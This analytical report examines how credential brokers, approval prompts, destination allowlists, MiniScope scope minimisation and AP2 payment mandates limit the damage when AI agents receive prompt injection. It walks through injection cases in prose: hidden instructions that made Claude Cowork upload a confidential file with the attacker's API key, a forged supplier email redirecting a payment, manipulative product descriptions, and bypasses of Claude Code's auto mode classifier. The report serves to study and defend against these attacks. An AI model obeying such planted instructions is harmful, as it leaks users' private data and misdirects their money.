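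The difference can be written in terms of four times, measured from the moment the attack succeeds. Let *e* be the time until the token expires, *v* the time until the service stops accepting it after someone revokes it, *s* the time until the agent's session ends, and *g* the time until someone withdraws the agent's permission. An attacker can use a stolen token for

*T*(theft) = min(*e*, *v*)

and can misuse the grant through the agent for up to

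*T*(misuse) = min(*s*, *g*)

The token's lifetime *e* does not appear in the second expression because the broker replaces each token when it expires. With 60-second tokens and an hour left in the session, a thief can use a stolen token for at most a minute, but an injected instruction may be able to misuse the agent's access for the whole hour. Many harmful actions need only one request. Hartman's draft acknowledges that even a short-lived token can do significant damage if misused, and recommends monitoring how agents use tokens after the broker issues them.

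#### Audience limits

An audience limit makes a token valid at only one service. *OAuth 2.0 Demonstrating Proof of Possession (DPoP)*, by Fett, Campbell and colleagues, describes the attack this prevents, in which a malicious or compromised service collects the tokens that clients send it and uses them at other services. The limit does not stop an agent from misusing a payment token at the payment service, because the token is valid there.

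#### Sender-constrained tokens

The same standard defines DPoP, one way to make sender-constrained tokens. For every request, the client signs a short statement with its secret key. The statement contains the request's method and web address, the time, a unique identifier and a fingerprint of the token. The service rejects the request if the signature does not match the key the token is bound to.

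When an agent misuses its grant, its own software signs the request, so the signature is valid. Fett and colleagues considered the equivalent problem in browsers, where an attacker's script runs inside the legitimate application and uses its signing key. They concluded that keeping such scripts out was most likely the only feasible defence at this level, and declared the problem out of scope. For an agent, the corresponding defence would be to prevent prompt injection, which nobody can yet do reliably.

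The signed statement also omits the body of the request. If a payment request gives the payee's account there, DPoP provides no evidence about the payee. The standard allows developers to extend the statement, but signing the body would still not prevent misuse, because the agent's software would sign whatever account number the model had chosen.

### Theft and misuse compared

| | Stolen credential | Grant misused through an agent with a broker |
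|---|---|---|
| Duration | Until the credential expires or the service rejects it | While the agent is running, still follows the planted text and still has permission |
| Location | Any machine, unless the token is bound to its sender | Only the agent's own environment, and only services for which the broker supplies access |
| Volume | As many requests as the service accepts | As many as the agent, or a program it writes, sends before something stops it |
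| Revocation | Replacing the credential shuts the thief out | Replacing the credential has no effect; someone must stop the agent, withdraw its permission or remove the planted text |

Stealing a credential is worse in most respects than misusing it through the agent, so brokers are worth having, but misuse can also involve many requests. An agent that chooses each action separately is slow, but one that can run code might follow an injected instruction to write a loop that sends thousands of requests, and the proxy would authenticate each of them.

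The difference in duration also shrinks if an agent runs repeatedly. Anthropic's *New in Claude Managed Agents* introduced agents that start on a schedule, for work such as a nightly data transfer. If every nightly run reads a web page with a planted instruction, the attacker gets a new opportunity each time without keeping anything from the previous run.

A security team that suspects a leak will normally replace the key. In Managed Agents, running sessions pick up the new key on their next call, which is convenient for ordinary maintenance but also lets a misdirected agent carry on as before. To cut off the agent's access, the team would have to delete the credential from the vault or stop the session.

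Revoking permission takes effect fastest when every request passes through the broker. Sweeney requires the broker to block a revoked agent within one second and any agent it delegated its authority to within five. When agents present tokens directly, some services keep relying on an earlier decision for a while. Hartman lists this delay as a threat he can reduce but not remove.

### Brokers that also judge requests

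A proxy that handles every request is well placed to refuse some of them. Bu (2026) argues on an IETF mailing list that if a separate component uses the credentials, it can enforce a narrow policy even when prompt injection has confused the agent's planning. The broker then hides the key and also performs per-call authorization, checking each proposed call with its actual values.

Vercel's firewall can do a simple version of this. According to Vercel's *Sandbox firewall*, a developer can have it attach a key only to requests with a certain path, method, query or header. In one example, it adds the key to POST requests whose path begins with "/v1/" and rejects all others with a 403 error.

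The final refusal has to be a rule of its own. Without it, a request that matches no rule still reaches the service, but without the company's key. An attacker could then have the agent attach the *attacker's* key to such a request and upload files to the attacker's account at the same service. The list of permitted destinations would not prevent this, because the service is on it.

These built-in conditions do not cover the body of a request. To check the body, the developer can have the firewall forward requests to the company's own proxy, which can read the contents and reject any requests that break its rules. The company has to write and maintain those rules.

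Sweeney puts limits into the agent's token instead. An example token permits two read operations on one Google Drive folder, with at most ten calls in total and ten megabytes per response. An injected instruction could not make this agent delete a file or open another folder, and the cap on calls would stop a loop. The instruction could still make the agent read the folder for the attacker's purposes. Sweeney accepts this, writing that an injected agent can exercise only the capabilities it already has.

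Another approach is to remove the choice the attacker wants to influence. Ubl and Arora advise that an agent helping one customer should have a tool that opens only that customer's data. If the tool took a customer number, a planted instruction could lead the agent to enter a different one.

#### The agent's stated reason

Hartman's form for requesting access from the broker has a field for the agent's reason, but he forbids the policy component to consider it. The component must decide from the agent's identity, the requested action and scope, the agent's past behaviour and the level of approval the action requires. The stated reason goes into the log for investigators to read after an incident.

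He excludes the agent's explanation because a compromised agent could write whatever reason was most likely to win approval. The explanation can also be false without any intent to deceive. An agent fooled by a forged email will write that it is paying a supplier whose bank details have changed. In both cases the explanation comes from the same model that read the attacker's text, so it is not independent evidence.

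Hartman claims that this removes the risk entirely if developers follow the draft. That seems too strong, because the draft sends moderate-risk requests to a human approver and shows the approver the agent's reason, among other things. A persuasive reason can influence a person as well as a program. The draft would be more consistent if it showed approvers the user's original request, taken from a record the agent could not edit.

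Excluding the reason also has a drawback, because the remaining inputs contain no trusted account of the task. In his SANS article, Hartman has the policy component check whether the scope is appropriate for the task. The draft's permitted inputs would let it check whether an action is normal for this agent, but not whether the scope fits the task.

### The invoice example with a broker

Suppose the company in the invoice example moves its mail and payment tokens into a broker. The agent reads the forged email and proposes to pay $4,200 to A-999. The attacker can still receive the money under all three designs. With Vercel's, the firewall recognises the payment service and attaches the token. With Anthropic's, the proxy gets the token from the vault and makes the call. With Hartman's preferred model, the agent asks the policy component for permission to make a payment. The request matches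 normal behaviour, because a known agent is requesting an ordinary action in the week when it usually pays invoices. If the company has classed such payments as low-risk, the agent receives a token for 60 seconds, which is long enough to make the payment.

The broker would defeat a different email, one that told the agent to send its payment token to the attacker. This could prevent a much larger loss. A thief with a token valid for an hour could take $600,000 by making one $10,000 payment a minute, if the account held that much. An attacker who has to work through the agent can send more false invoices, but each has to look plausible and gives the company another chance to notice the fraud.

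To stop the payment to A-999, the broker would have to check the payee. If the payment service puts the payee in the web address, as in "/payees/S-100/payments", Vercel's firewall could attach the token to requests for that path and refuse all others. If the account number is in the request body, the company needs its own proxy with a rule about which accounts are permitted. Hartman's policy component could enforce a similar rule if the company treats each payee as a separate resource. If the component's record of past behaviour includes payees, it could also detect that A-999 is new and send the request to a person, then refuse it if nobody answers within five minutes.

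That person would see the proposed payment and the agent's explanation that the supplier has changed banks, but would still have to call the supplier to confirm the change, using a number that did not come from the email.

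## Claude Code and Claude Cowork: approval prompts and permitted destinations

A broker that only hides keys does not stop the agent from making requests it shouldn't. Anthropic has tried to control this in its own products by asking the user before the agent acts and by limiting which internet addresses the agent can reach. In May 2026 it described where both fell short. Users of Claude Code approved almost every prompt they saw. In Claude Cowork, the company's agent for general office work, planted instructions got Claude to send private files to an address that Anthropic had permitted.

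### What the approval figures measure

At first, Claude Code could read files freely but had to ask the user before it changed a file, ran a command or used the network. Within weeks, users were paying less attention to the prompts. Anthropic added a sandbox that lets commands read files but write only inside the project folder, and that blocks network access by default. Most commands can therefore run without a prompt. Anthropic later added auto mode, in which a separate classifier model allows or blocks actions in the user's place. Auto mode became the default for new sessions on most individual and team plans on 14 August, according to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026).

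Anthropic's account gives four figures for these measures. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* explains how the company obtained the last two.

| Figure | What Anthropic counted | What the figure leaves open |
|---|---|---|
| 93% | Permission prompts that users approved | How many of the approved actions were harmful |
| 84% | The fall in the number of prompts with the sandbox on, in Anthropic's internal use | Whether users read the remaining prompts more carefully |
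| 17% | Actions the classifier wrongly allowed, out of 52 real overeager ones | How often it would miss an action that an attacker had planned |
| 0.4% | Harmless actions the classifier blocked, in a sample of 10,000 real tool calls by employees | How many harmful actions it would catch |

None of these is the rate at which prompt injections succeed. An overeager action is one that Claude takes on its own initiative and that goes beyond what the user authorized, such as deleting branches from a shared server when asked to "clean up old branches". No attacker is involved. If an injection gets the model to propose a harmful action with probability *p*, and the check lets that action through with probability *m*, the attack succeeds with probability

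*p* × *m*

The 17% estimates *m* for a different kind of action and doesn't measure *p*. It is also imprecise, because it comes from only nine of 52 actions. If those 52 were a random sample, the true rate could plausibly be anywhere from about 9% to 30%. The classifier missed 5.7% of 1,000 artificial attempts to send data out, which more closely resemble an attacker's goals.

Most commands are harmless and deserve approval, so the 93% approval rate does not prove that users were careless. An experiment that Anthropic commissioned is better evidence. A research company had 1,053 paid testers work on coding tasks and replaced one permission prompt in each session with a clearly dangerous command. The testers refused it 13.6% of the time, while auto mode blocked 89% of the same commands. The testers' refusal rate fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

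The testers were not working on their own projects and had little to lose, so developers might do better on code they care about. In this test, though, human approval added very little to auto mode. Auto mode blocked 800 commands that a tester approved, while testers refused only six that auto mode allowed. Using both would have stopped 943 of the 1,053 commands, compared with 937 for auto mode alone.

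Auto mode can also fail badly against a determined attacker. *Claude Code can be hijacked by a web page* (Constantin, 2026) reports that the security researcher Johann Rehberger got past auto mode in up to 80% of his attempts, and that Anthropic told him the product was working as designed. None of the 720 attempts in an evaluation commissioned by Anthropic had succeeded, but the testers had tuned those attacks to an older model.

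According to Anthropic's documentation, the sandbox is off by default and applies only to shell commands. Claude's own file tools and any MCP servers run outside it, so it would not restrict an attack like the one on the Pacman repository, which went through an MCP server.

### What an approver has to see

In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the classifier identified the danger but wrongly treated something the user had said as consent. A user who says "clean up the PR" has not agreed to a force-push, which overwrites a project's shared history. Approving one force-push also does not authorise the next. Approval is meaningful only if the approver sees the exact action, including its values and destination, and the software then runs only that action.

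An approval prompt that shows only a program's name does not meet this standard. If Claude asks to run a script called build.py, what happens depends on the script's contents, which Claude may have written a minute earlier. Auto mode's classifier is therefore supposed to judge the contents of a file that the agent writes and then runs. But in June 2026, nearly half of active command-line users had a standing rule that let Claude run some shell commands without asking. Many of these rules covered an interpreter such as Python, which in practice lets the agent run almost anything, and auto mode ignores rules that broad.

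An agent that routinely sends code to a team's private repository would leak the same code by sending it to a public one. Auto mode now checks whether the destination of a push or pull request is public, private or trusted. For the Pacman pull request, an approver would have needed to see that the repository was public and that the text came from private ones.

Approval must also come before any code runs. Between mid-2025 and January 2026, Anthropic received three reports of flaws that let code run before the user had agreed. In the simplest case, a downloaded project contained a settings file with a command to run at startup, and Claude Code read the file before asking whether the user trusted the folder. Claude Code now waits for the user's answer before reading such settings.

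The agent's own explanation is a poor basis for approval, as Hartman argued about brokers. Auto mode's classifier receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not Claude's explanations or the results that tools return. Claude's explanations therefore cannot influence its decisions, and text planted in a web page does not reach it directly. This also means the classifier often cannot determine where a value came from. If the agent asks to cancel a job that the user never named, the classifier cannot determine whether the agent looked up the job's identifier or made it up.

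Users reject 39% of the plans Claude presents but only 3% of permission prompts. This may mean that people review decisions more carefully when they understand them and make them less often, though they may also reject plans because they prefer a different approach. Approving a plan is still not a substitute for approving the action, because the agent writes the plan before it reads the material that supplies the action's values.

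An approval prompt doesn't help a user who can't interpret it, even if it is complete. Anthropic expects developers to understand shell commands but doesn't expect this of the office workers who use Cowork, so for them it relies more on fixed limits, including a list of permitted internet addresses.

### An upload with the attacker's own key

PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* describes an attack on Cowork two days after its release as a research preview. Willison (2026) linked to the disclosure on 14 January. PromptArmor, a security company, played both the victim and the attacker. As the victim, it gave Cowork access to a folder of confidential property documents. It also uploaded a document that appeared to contain instructions for analysing such files, of the kind people share online, and asked Cowork to use it.

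The document contained hidden instructions for Claude to upload the largest file it could find to Anthropic's Files API, which stores files for use with Claude. The instructions included the attacker's API key. Cowork ran commands in a virtual machine that blocked most internet addresses but allowed Anthropic's, which Cowork needs to work. Claude uploaded a loan estimate containing financial details and partial social security numbers to the attacker's Anthropic account. The user did not have to approve anything. PromptArmor used Claude Haiku, a smaller model, for this demonstration, and in a separate test got Claude Opus 4.5 to leak customer records the same way.

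The attack depended on permissions from three sources:

| Step | Permission or credential | Who supplied it |
|---|---|---|
| Read the loan estimate | Access to the folder | The user |
| Connect to Anthropic's API | The list of permitted addresses | Anthropic |
| Store the file in an account | An API key for that account | The attacker |
| Open the file afterwards | The same key | The attacker |

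The attack misused the agent's permission to read the user's folder and use the network. The attacker had neither access to the folder nor a way to get data out of the virtual machine, but the agent had both. The key belonged to the attacker, who already had the right to store files in their own account. The attacker did not steal a credential or use the user's credential through the agent, so keeping the user's tokens in a vault would have made no difference. Cowork already kept the user's credentials outside the virtual machine.

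Rehberger had reported the same weakness in Claude's chat product three months earlier. According to his account, Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate*, Anthropic closed the report within an hour on 25 October 2025 as a model safety issue outside the scope of its security programme. Five days later, it confirmed that such reports were in scope. Rehberger suggested letting the sandbox communicate only with the logged-in user's account. Oasis Security also found the Files API route in the chat product, as part of a longer attack.

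### Why a permitted address is a grant

Anthropic had thought of its list as a filter on destinations. The filter worked correctly in this attack, since the address was on the list. Anthropic now regards each entry as a grant of every function that the agent can reach there. Let *D* be the set of permitted addresses, *F*(*d*) the functions available at address *d*, and *K*(*d*) the credentials that the service at *d* accepts. A filter that checks only the address permits every request in

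{(*d*, *f*, *k*) : *d* ∈ *D*, *f* ∈ *F*(*d*), *k* ∈ *K*(*d*)}

Anthropic allowed Cowork to connect to one address so that it could send prompts to the model with its own credential. The Files API was at the same address, and the service accepted any customer's key, so Cowork could also upload files to any customer's account.

Many ordinary allowlist entries have the same problem. PromptArmor's *What domains should I add to my allowlist?* (2026) points out that developers permit npm, a library of software packages, so that agents can download from it, but anyone with a free account can publish there. GitHub lets anyone create a public repository. An entry that covers every address under a cloud provider's domain also covers servers an attacker rents from that provider. Docker, which also makes sandboxes for agents, warns that its network filter checks the domain but does not inspect the traffic.

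The Cowork fix narrows *K*(*d*) for Anthropic's address. A proxy in the virtual machine intercepts API requests and forwards only those carrying the token that Anthropic issued for that session, so it rejects the attacker's key. The proxy also blocks headers that could make the server fetch material from elsewhere. Anthropic put this check in the virtual machine because its servers could not tell Cowork's requests apart from those sent by any other customer's program.

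Companies can apply a similar rule to their whole network. With tenant restrictions, a feature for enterprise customers, the company's proxy adds a header that lists the organizations whose accounts its users may access. Anthropic then refuses access for any other organization, including access with an API key. This works only for traffic that goes through the company's proxy. According to Anthropic's *Claude Cowork architecture overview*, Cowork sessions now run on Anthropic's servers by default, so their sandboxes' network traffic goes through a proxy that Anthropic operates.

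### What an attacker could still do with the session's token

With the fix in place, a planted instruction can still make the agent send any request the session's token allows. If the token covers file storage, the agent could upload the loan estimate to the user's own account, though the attacker could not open it without a further step, such as getting the file shared. The instruction could also make the agent use up the user's allowance or, if the token permitted it, change or delete stored material. Anthropic describes the token as limited in scope and valid for one session, so the possible damage depends on how narrow the scope is.

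Misuse can continue after the token expires if an injection gets the agent to write an instruction into a file that later sessions read. Each new session will then load the instruction and supply a new token. Anthropic lists this kind of persistence among the risks it expects to grow.

The token check covers only one address, and an attacker may not need any address on the list. According to Anthropic's *Use Claude Cowork safely*, the network limits do not apply to web search, web fetching or MCP connections, including the one that operates the user's browser. If the user has connected an email account that can send messages, an attacker could plant an instruction for Claude to email the loan estimate. Auto mode might block the email, but it does not screen connected tools that the user has set to "Always allow" unless the connector marks them as destructive. Organizations can turn off permanent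 approvals and require a new decision for each restricted call, but that brings back the problem of too many prompts.

### What logs can show afterwards

Logs are of limited help in finding such misuse. Anthropic writes that once planted text has led an agent to leak data, the log "just shows a successful, authorized API call". If a log recorded only the time, address and result of the Cowork upload, the upload would look like normal use of the product.

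The Cowork attack left a record, so Anthropic's conclusion that there is no signal to find after the event is too strong for that case. Anyone who expanded the command in the Cowork window could see the complete request, including the attacker's key. Pluto Security found that Cowork also kept detailed logs, including full commands, on the user's computer, and that some of them remained after the user deleted the session. An investigator who compared the key in the command with the company's own keys would have had clear evidence of the attack. However, if an attack uses the session's own token, there is no attacker's key to find.

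Enterprise customers can now retrieve transcripts of each session's prompts, responses and tool calls, according to Anthropic's *Compliance API coverage extends to Claude Cowork and Claude Code*. These are much more useful than a list of network connections, because an investigator can see what the agent read before it acted. But if an agent reads fifty emails and then sends a file, the investigator still has to judge which email, if any, prompted the agent to send it, and can only do so after the file has gone.

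A written record of an attack can also spread it to agents that read the record. After the February test in which a researcher tricked an employee into running a malicious prompt, Anthropic's staff posted the prompt in Slack to discuss it. Someone then pointed out that some of the company's agents read Slack, so the staff added a unique string to the thread that would help them notice if an agent picked up the text.

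### Approval and destination limits in the invoice example

Suppose the company in the invoice example requires a person to approve the $4,200 payment. Whether this helps depends largely on what the prompt displays:

| Prompt | What the approver could notice |
|---|---|
| Allow the agent to use the payment tool? | Nothing, since the user asked for payments |
| Pay the supplier's invoice for $4,200? | Nothing, since the company owes this money |
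| Pay $4,200 to account A-999? | The wrong account, if the approver remembers or looks up S-100 |
| Pay $4,200 to account A-999? All earlier payments to this supplier went to S-100. | The change of account |

Only the last prompt gives a busy person a reason to call the supplier. The payment history in that prompt must come from the company's records, because an agent that relies on the email might describe A-999 as the supplier's usual account. The software must also take the account number from the pending request and lock it, so the agent cannot change the payee after the person approves.

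The company could keep prompts infrequent by showing this one only when a payee is new. But the testers in Anthropic's study approved most of the dangerous commands even early in their sessions, so rarity alone will not make people careful. Requiring the approver to record a phone call to the supplier would be safer than a single button.

A classifier like the one in auto mode would have trouble judging this payment. It would receive the user's request to pay the week's invoices and the call that pays A-999, but not the email or any supplier records that the agent had looked up. Because the user named no account, the classifier would block payments to S-100 as well if it treated every value chosen by the agent as unauthorized, and it would allow A-999 if it accepted any account as part of paying invoices.

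Limits on destinations would stop the agent from uploading the company's mailbox to an attacker's server if a different email told it to. They would not stop the fraudulent payment, because the request goes to the company's usual payment service. The check from the Cowork fix would not stop it either, because the request carries the company's own token.

The attacker's account number works here like the attacker's API key in Cowork, since each directs something valuable to an account the attacker controls. Anthropic could fix Cowork with a simple comparison because each session had only one correct token, which the software knew in advance. But a company pays many suppliers, and some of them change banks, so its software needs a list of correct accounts that an email cannot alter.

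## MiniScope and the Agent Payments Protocol: a grant for one task or one purchase

Approval prompts and lists of permitted destinations don't narrow an agent's grant. A narrower grant would reduce what an injected instruction could make the agent do. Under the principle of least privilege, a program should have only the permissions its job requires. MiniScope, a research system from the University of California, Berkeley and IBM Research, finds the narrowest OAuth scopes sufficient for a task. Google's Agent Payments Protocol (AP2) can limit a grant to one purchase from one merchant.

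Least privilege is hard to apply to agents because people value agents for their flexibility, so developers are tempted to give them broad access at the start. Surapani and colleagues list what a developer could restrict: the tools an agent can see, its use of a tool at a particular step, the values it passes, the data it gets back, and the authority it hands to other agents. MiniScope restricts which operations an agent can use, while AP2 also restricts values such as the payee and the amount.

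### How MiniScope chooses scopes

A scope usually allows several operations, or methods, and a service often accepts more than one scope for the same method. In Google Calendar, 24 of the 37 methods can be reached through different branches of the permission hierarchy. Picking the narrowest scope for each method separately therefore doesn't always give the narrowest set of scopes for the whole task.

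Zhu, Tseng and colleagues (2025), in *MiniScope*, begin with each service's public documentation, which lists the scopes that allow each method. Let *O*(*s*) be the set of methods that scope *s* allows. MiniScope places *s*₁ below *s*₂ in a hierarchy if

*O*(*s*₁) ⊆ *O*(*s*₂)

When the user makes a request, the agent's model writes a plan of the tool calls it expects to make. MiniScope then chooses the set of scopes with the lowest total cost:

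minimize Σ cost(*s*) · *x*ₛ

Here *x*ₛ is 1 if MiniScope selects scope *s* and 0 otherwise. The selected scopes must allow every method in the plan. In the paper, a scope's cost is the number of methods it allows, but developers can choose another measure.

Suppose a mail service has four methods and three scopes:

| Scope | Methods it allows | Cost |
|---|---|---|
| mail.read | list, get | 2 |
| mail.send | send | 1 |
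| mail.full | list, get, send, delete | 4 |

A user asks the agent to summarize the latest email from a supplier. The plan needs "list" and "get", which both mail.read and mail.full allow, and MiniScope chooses mail.read at a cost of 2. Another user asks the agent to reply to the email and then delete it. This task needs mail.full, the broadest scope, because no other scope allows deletion.

An agent in MiniScope starts with no permissions. If a plan needs a scope that the user has not granted, MiniScope describes the scope and offers four choices: always allow it, allow it once, allow it for this session, or refuse. It then gives the agent a session token and keeps the real credentials. Each tool call passes through a checker, which compares the method with the granted scopes and attaches the real credential only if they match. MiniScope therefore also works as a credential broker.

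Zhu and colleagues illustrate the protection with an email about a film night. The user asks the agent to reply, and MiniScope first requests permission only to read mail. The email contains an instruction to delete the message after replying and to add this step to the plan. When the agent revises its plan, MiniScope must request permission to send and delete mail. The user, who wanted only a reply, can see that something is wrong and refuse.

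This works because the injected action needs a scope that the legitimate task does not. In the invented mail service, though, a user who wanted to reply and delete has already granted mail.full, so an injected instruction to send the attacker a copy of another email would need no further permission, and MiniScope would allow it.

### What the MiniScope tests measured

Zhu and colleagues tested MiniScope on ten real applications, including Gmail, Slack, Dropbox and Zoom. Each has between 32 and 247 methods, far more than the simulated applications in most earlier tests. They had no records of real users' requests, so they had a language model invent some. The simplest requests used a single method in one application, while others involved three applications.

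The MiniScope paper compares its system with an agent that had no controls, one that asked permission for each method, and one that used a second language model to choose the scopes. Proprietary models chose the same scopes as MiniScope in 70–83% of cases, and open-source models in 20–34%. The models' most common error was choosing overly broad scopes. On average, their choices allowed 1.03 to 2.19 times as many methods as MiniScope's, depending on the model and the type of task.

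MiniScope added 1–6% to running time. Tasks across several applications took 5.23 seconds on average, compared with 4.91 with no controls and 20.50 when a language model chose the scopes. These figures exclude the time users spend answering prompts. In a simulation of three months of Gmail use, between 18% and 60% of requests required confirmation, depending on how cautious the simulated user was. Even 18% is a lot of interruptions for someone who uses an agent all day, and a user who reduces them by choosing "Always allow" gives up much of the benefit.

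The comparison of scope choices treats MiniScope's own answer as correct, so it cannot reveal mistakes in how MiniScope measures a permission's breadth. MiniScope counts the methods each scope allows. In Google Calendar, the scope for reading events on calendars the user owns allows more methods than the general scope for reading events, so MiniScope ranks it as broader. For a task that either scope would cover, MiniScope would choose the general one, even though it may expose more people's events.

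A task may also have no single smallest grant. *Incomparable Minima in Agent Tool Authorization* (2026) notes that Zhu and colleagues do not discuss whether MiniScope's solution is unique. If two sets of scopes are both enough for a task and neither contains the other, MiniScope uses its cost formula to choose between them, and another reasonable formula might lead to a different choice.

The experiments didn't measure how often MiniScope stops an attack, but they did show that six connectors for ChatGPT and Claude requested more access than their advertised tools needed. ChatGPT's Gmail connector, for example, advertised only tools for reading email but requested scopes that allowed 50 methods, including ones that change and delete email. MiniScope found that scopes allowing 32 methods would have been enough. A developer can remove these extra permissions once for all users, without asking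 them anything.

### Standards for asking for less

Zhu and colleagues enforce their limits in software between the agent and the service. Two extensions to OAuth can instead put a smaller grant in the token itself, so that the service enforces it.

*RFC 8693*, by Jones, Nadalin and colleagues, defines token exchange, in which a program sends its token to the authorization server and receives a different one. The program can specify which service and scope it wants for the new token. For example, a main agent whose token gives full access to a mailbox could exchange it for one that can only read mail, then pass the new token to an agent that writes summaries. The new token can also record that the agent is acting for a particular user, according to API Evangelist's *OAuth 2.0 Token Exchange (RFC 8693)*. Token exchange is useful for the handovers between agents that Surapani and colleagues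 describe, but a narrower scope such as "payments" still doesn't limit whom the agent can pay.

Rich Authorization Requests, which Lodderstedt, Richer and Campbell define in *RFC 9396*, can limit it. The client puts the details in a parameter called authorization_details. The sample in the IETF's text of *RFC 9396* requests a transfer of €123.50 to one merchant's account. Adapted to the invoice example, such a request might look like this:

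```json
{
  "type": "payment_initiation",
  "actions": ["initiate"],
  "instructedAmount": {
    "currency": "USD",
    "amount": "4200.00"
  },
  "creditorName": "Regular supplier",
  "creditorAccount": { "id": "S-100" }
}
```

The authorization server can show these details to the user and issue a token only for this payment. If the agent tried to use the token to pay A-999, or to pay $9,000 to S-100, the payment service could refuse.

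For this to work, the client and the service must agree on what each type of request contains. The draft *OAuth 2.0 RAR Metadata and Error Signaling* (Zehavi, 2026) explains that the standard gives clients no way to discover this, so they rely on separate arrangements with each service. The draft would let clients look up the format automatically and learn what to request after a refusal. Until services adopt something like it, a bank and its partners can agree on a payment format, but a general-purpose agent connecting to an unfamiliar service will usually have to use scopes. MiniScope also uses scopes, because those are what its ten applications publish.

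*Beyond OAuth* (2026) describes PAuth, a system meant to avoid this dependence on each service. PAuth turns the user's ordinary-language request into a permission for particular operations with particular values, and software outside the tools enforces it without changing them. In tests on AgentDojo and a separate deployment of the agent OpenClaw, PAuth allowed every legitimate task and blocked every adversarial call. That is much better than trained resistance usually does, but it depends on the request being specific enough. Surapani and colleagues warn that a task can be ambiguous and that a manipulated prompt may lead to a broader permission than the user intended. For example, "Pay this week's invoices" does not include an account number, so the system has to get it from somewhere else.

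### What an AP2 mandate contains

Google announced AP2 in September 2025 as an open protocol for purchases by agents. AP2's *Security and Privacy Considerations* assumes that preventing prompt injection is infeasible and that any agent could be an attacker. The protocol therefore depends on signed documents called mandates, which ordinary software can check without relying on the model.

AP2's *Agentic Payment Protocol (v0.2)* defines two kinds of mandate. A Checkout Mandate covers the goods and goes to the merchant. A Payment Mandate covers the money and goes to the credential provider, such as a digital wallet, and sometimes to the card network. The merchant signs the order first, and both mandates then include a cryptographic hash of the signed order, a short value that changes if anyone alters the order. This prevents anyone from attaching the payment to a different order.

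If the user is present, the agent prepares the mandates, and a separate screen shows the final order and payment for approval. AP2 calls this screen the trusted surface and forbids language models in it. After the user approves, the software behind the screen signs both mandates with a key belonging to the user or the agent's provider. The agent must not have access to this key.

If the user will be away, they approve limits in advance. The resulting "open" mandates contain the limits and the agent's public key. When the agent finds a suitable order, it signs "closed" mandates for that order with its own key and presents them together with the open ones. In an example from AP2's *Agent Payments Protocol Documentation*, the agent may buy one pair of gold sneakers from one merchant for up to $200 within an hour, and it finds them for $199.

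| | User present | User absent |
|---|---|---|
| What the user approves | The final order and payment | Limits on a future order and payment |
| Who signs the final mandates | The user's key or the agent provider's key | The agent's key, backed by the signed limits |
| What the merchant checks | The signature, and that the order matches its own | The same, plus permitted items and merchants |
| What the wallet or network checks | The signature on the payment | The same, plus limits such as the payee, amount and date |

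The payment processor must also check that the payment credential is valid for this order. An open Payment Mandate can permit repeated payments and set a total budget for them. If the software checking a mandate doesn't recognise one of its limits, the check must fail. The merchant can then ask for the user to come back and approve the purchase directly.

These checks give a merchant or bank much better evidence than an ordinary OAuth token does. The merchant or bank can confirm that the user, or a provider the user trusts, approved certain limits and that the purchase falls within them. The checks do not show why the agent chose this product, or whether the user would have wanted those limits after a closer look.

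AP2 protects less well against spending twice than against changing an order. An agent must not present the same open mandate for another purchase until it receives a signed rejection of the first. AP2 relies mainly on conventional code around the agent's model to enforce this rule. The wallet, network and processor may reject overlapping purchases but do not have to. An attacker who got past the agent's code could therefore make a second purchase unless one of these companies had chosen to check.

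### A product description that changed the agent's choice

In *Whispers of Wealth*, Debi, Zhu and Sen Gupta (2026) tested an AP2 shopping system with prompt injection. They built four agents on Google's Gemini 2.5 Flash: one to shop, one to represent the merchant, one to process payments and one to supply the user's details. In every trial, the user asked for outdoor basketball shoes.

In the Branded Whisper attack, a dishonest merchant hid an instruction in a product description telling the agent to rank that product first. The product came first in none of the ten trials without the instruction and in all ten with it. In six of the trials with the instruction, the ranking clearly contradicted something the user had asked for, such as a brand. In the other four, the product fit the request well enough that the instruction's effect is harder to distinguish from an ordinary recommendation.

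In the Vault Whisper attack, a malicious user used direct injection to try to obtain other customers' details. The attack succeeded in two of ten trials, and in three more the system partly attempted to retrieve the data. In one failure, the agent accepted an identity the user had typed, without checking it, and looked up that person's data. This is a serious flaw in the test system, but it has little to do with mandates, which control purchases, not access to customer records. Conventional access control in the customer database should have stopped the attack.

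The rates are imprecise because there were so few trials. At the 95% confidence level, ten successes out of ten are compatible with a true rate as low as about 69%, and two out of ten with anything from about 3% to 56%. The success rate for the product attack also counts rankings, not purchases, so a user who read the list carefully might still have picked another pair of shoes.

In the product attack, Debi and colleagues used an earlier version of AP2 with three mandates, which PayPal also describes. The user first approved an Intent Mandate with their general request. The agent then read the merchant's product descriptions, including the planted instruction. After that, the user would approve a Cart Mandate for the particular shoes and a Payment Mandate. The attack therefore came between the first approval and the other two, and it broke none of the signatures.

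So a user who is present gets another chance to notice the bad choice. An absent user signs the open mandates before the agent reads the product descriptions, and the agent signs the rest. If an injection influenced the agent's choice, the user might not find out until the shoes arrived.

### Later versions and research

Google released version 0.2 of AP2 in April 2026, adding support for payments while the user is absent, and donated the protocol to the FIDO Alliance, an industry group best known for work on replacing passwords. AP2's documentation still described version 0.2 in late August. A FIDO working group is developing payment specifications from AP2 and a related Mastercard framework, according to PYMNTS's *Google and Mastercard Contribute Agentic Commerce Standards to FIDO Alliance*, so the eventual standard may differ from both.

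Version 0.2 of AP2 doesn't prevent the Branded Whisper attack, but its documentation covers the same threat under the name "manipulated discovery". AP2 offers two safeguards. The merchant's signature guarantees that nobody has altered the offer, but it doesn't help here because the merchant is the attacker and can sign its own offer. The user's limits do help, because they cap the loss if the agent chooses badly. An agent with permission to spend $200 on shoes cannot spend $2,000 on a watch, even if a product description contains instructions to do so.

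*Zero-Trust Runtime Verification for Agentic Payment Protocols* (February 2026) examines attacks that reuse a valid mandate or use it in the wrong context. Version 0.2 addresses some of these attacks by tying each open mandate to the agent's key and each closed mandate to both the open one and a particular order. *Beyond the Mandate* (August 2026), a security analysis, lists manipulation of a mandate's contents as a possible attacker goal and classifies it as damage to the integrity of the user's signed intent. Signing protects the contents from later changes, but it doesn't help if they were already false when the user signed them.

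### Misuse that fits the grant

Let *G* be the set of actions a grant allows, *T* the set of actions that fit the task as the grant describes it, and *H* the set of actions that serve the attacker. An injected instruction can lead the agent to carry out any action in

*G* ∩ *H*

If *G* is larger than *T*, MiniScope or AP2 can remove the excess. But a grant that lets the agent do the whole task must include all of *T*, so even a perfectly fitted grant still allows

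*T* ∩ *H*

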